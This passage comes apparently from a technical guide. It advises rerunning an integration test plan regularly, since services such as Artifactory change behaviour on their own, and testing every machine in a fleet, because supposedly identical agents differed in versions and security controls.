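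The approved services change independently of the adapter. For example, since an update on October 26, Artifactory has responded to anonymous requests for restricted packages by prompting the client for credentials. A team can't expect a warning before every such change, so it should also run the test plan regularly, perhaps weekly.

The tests have to cover every machine. In Maiti's fleet, agents that were supposed to be alike ran different versions of the same software and had different security controls, so passing the tests on one machine would have shown little about the others.
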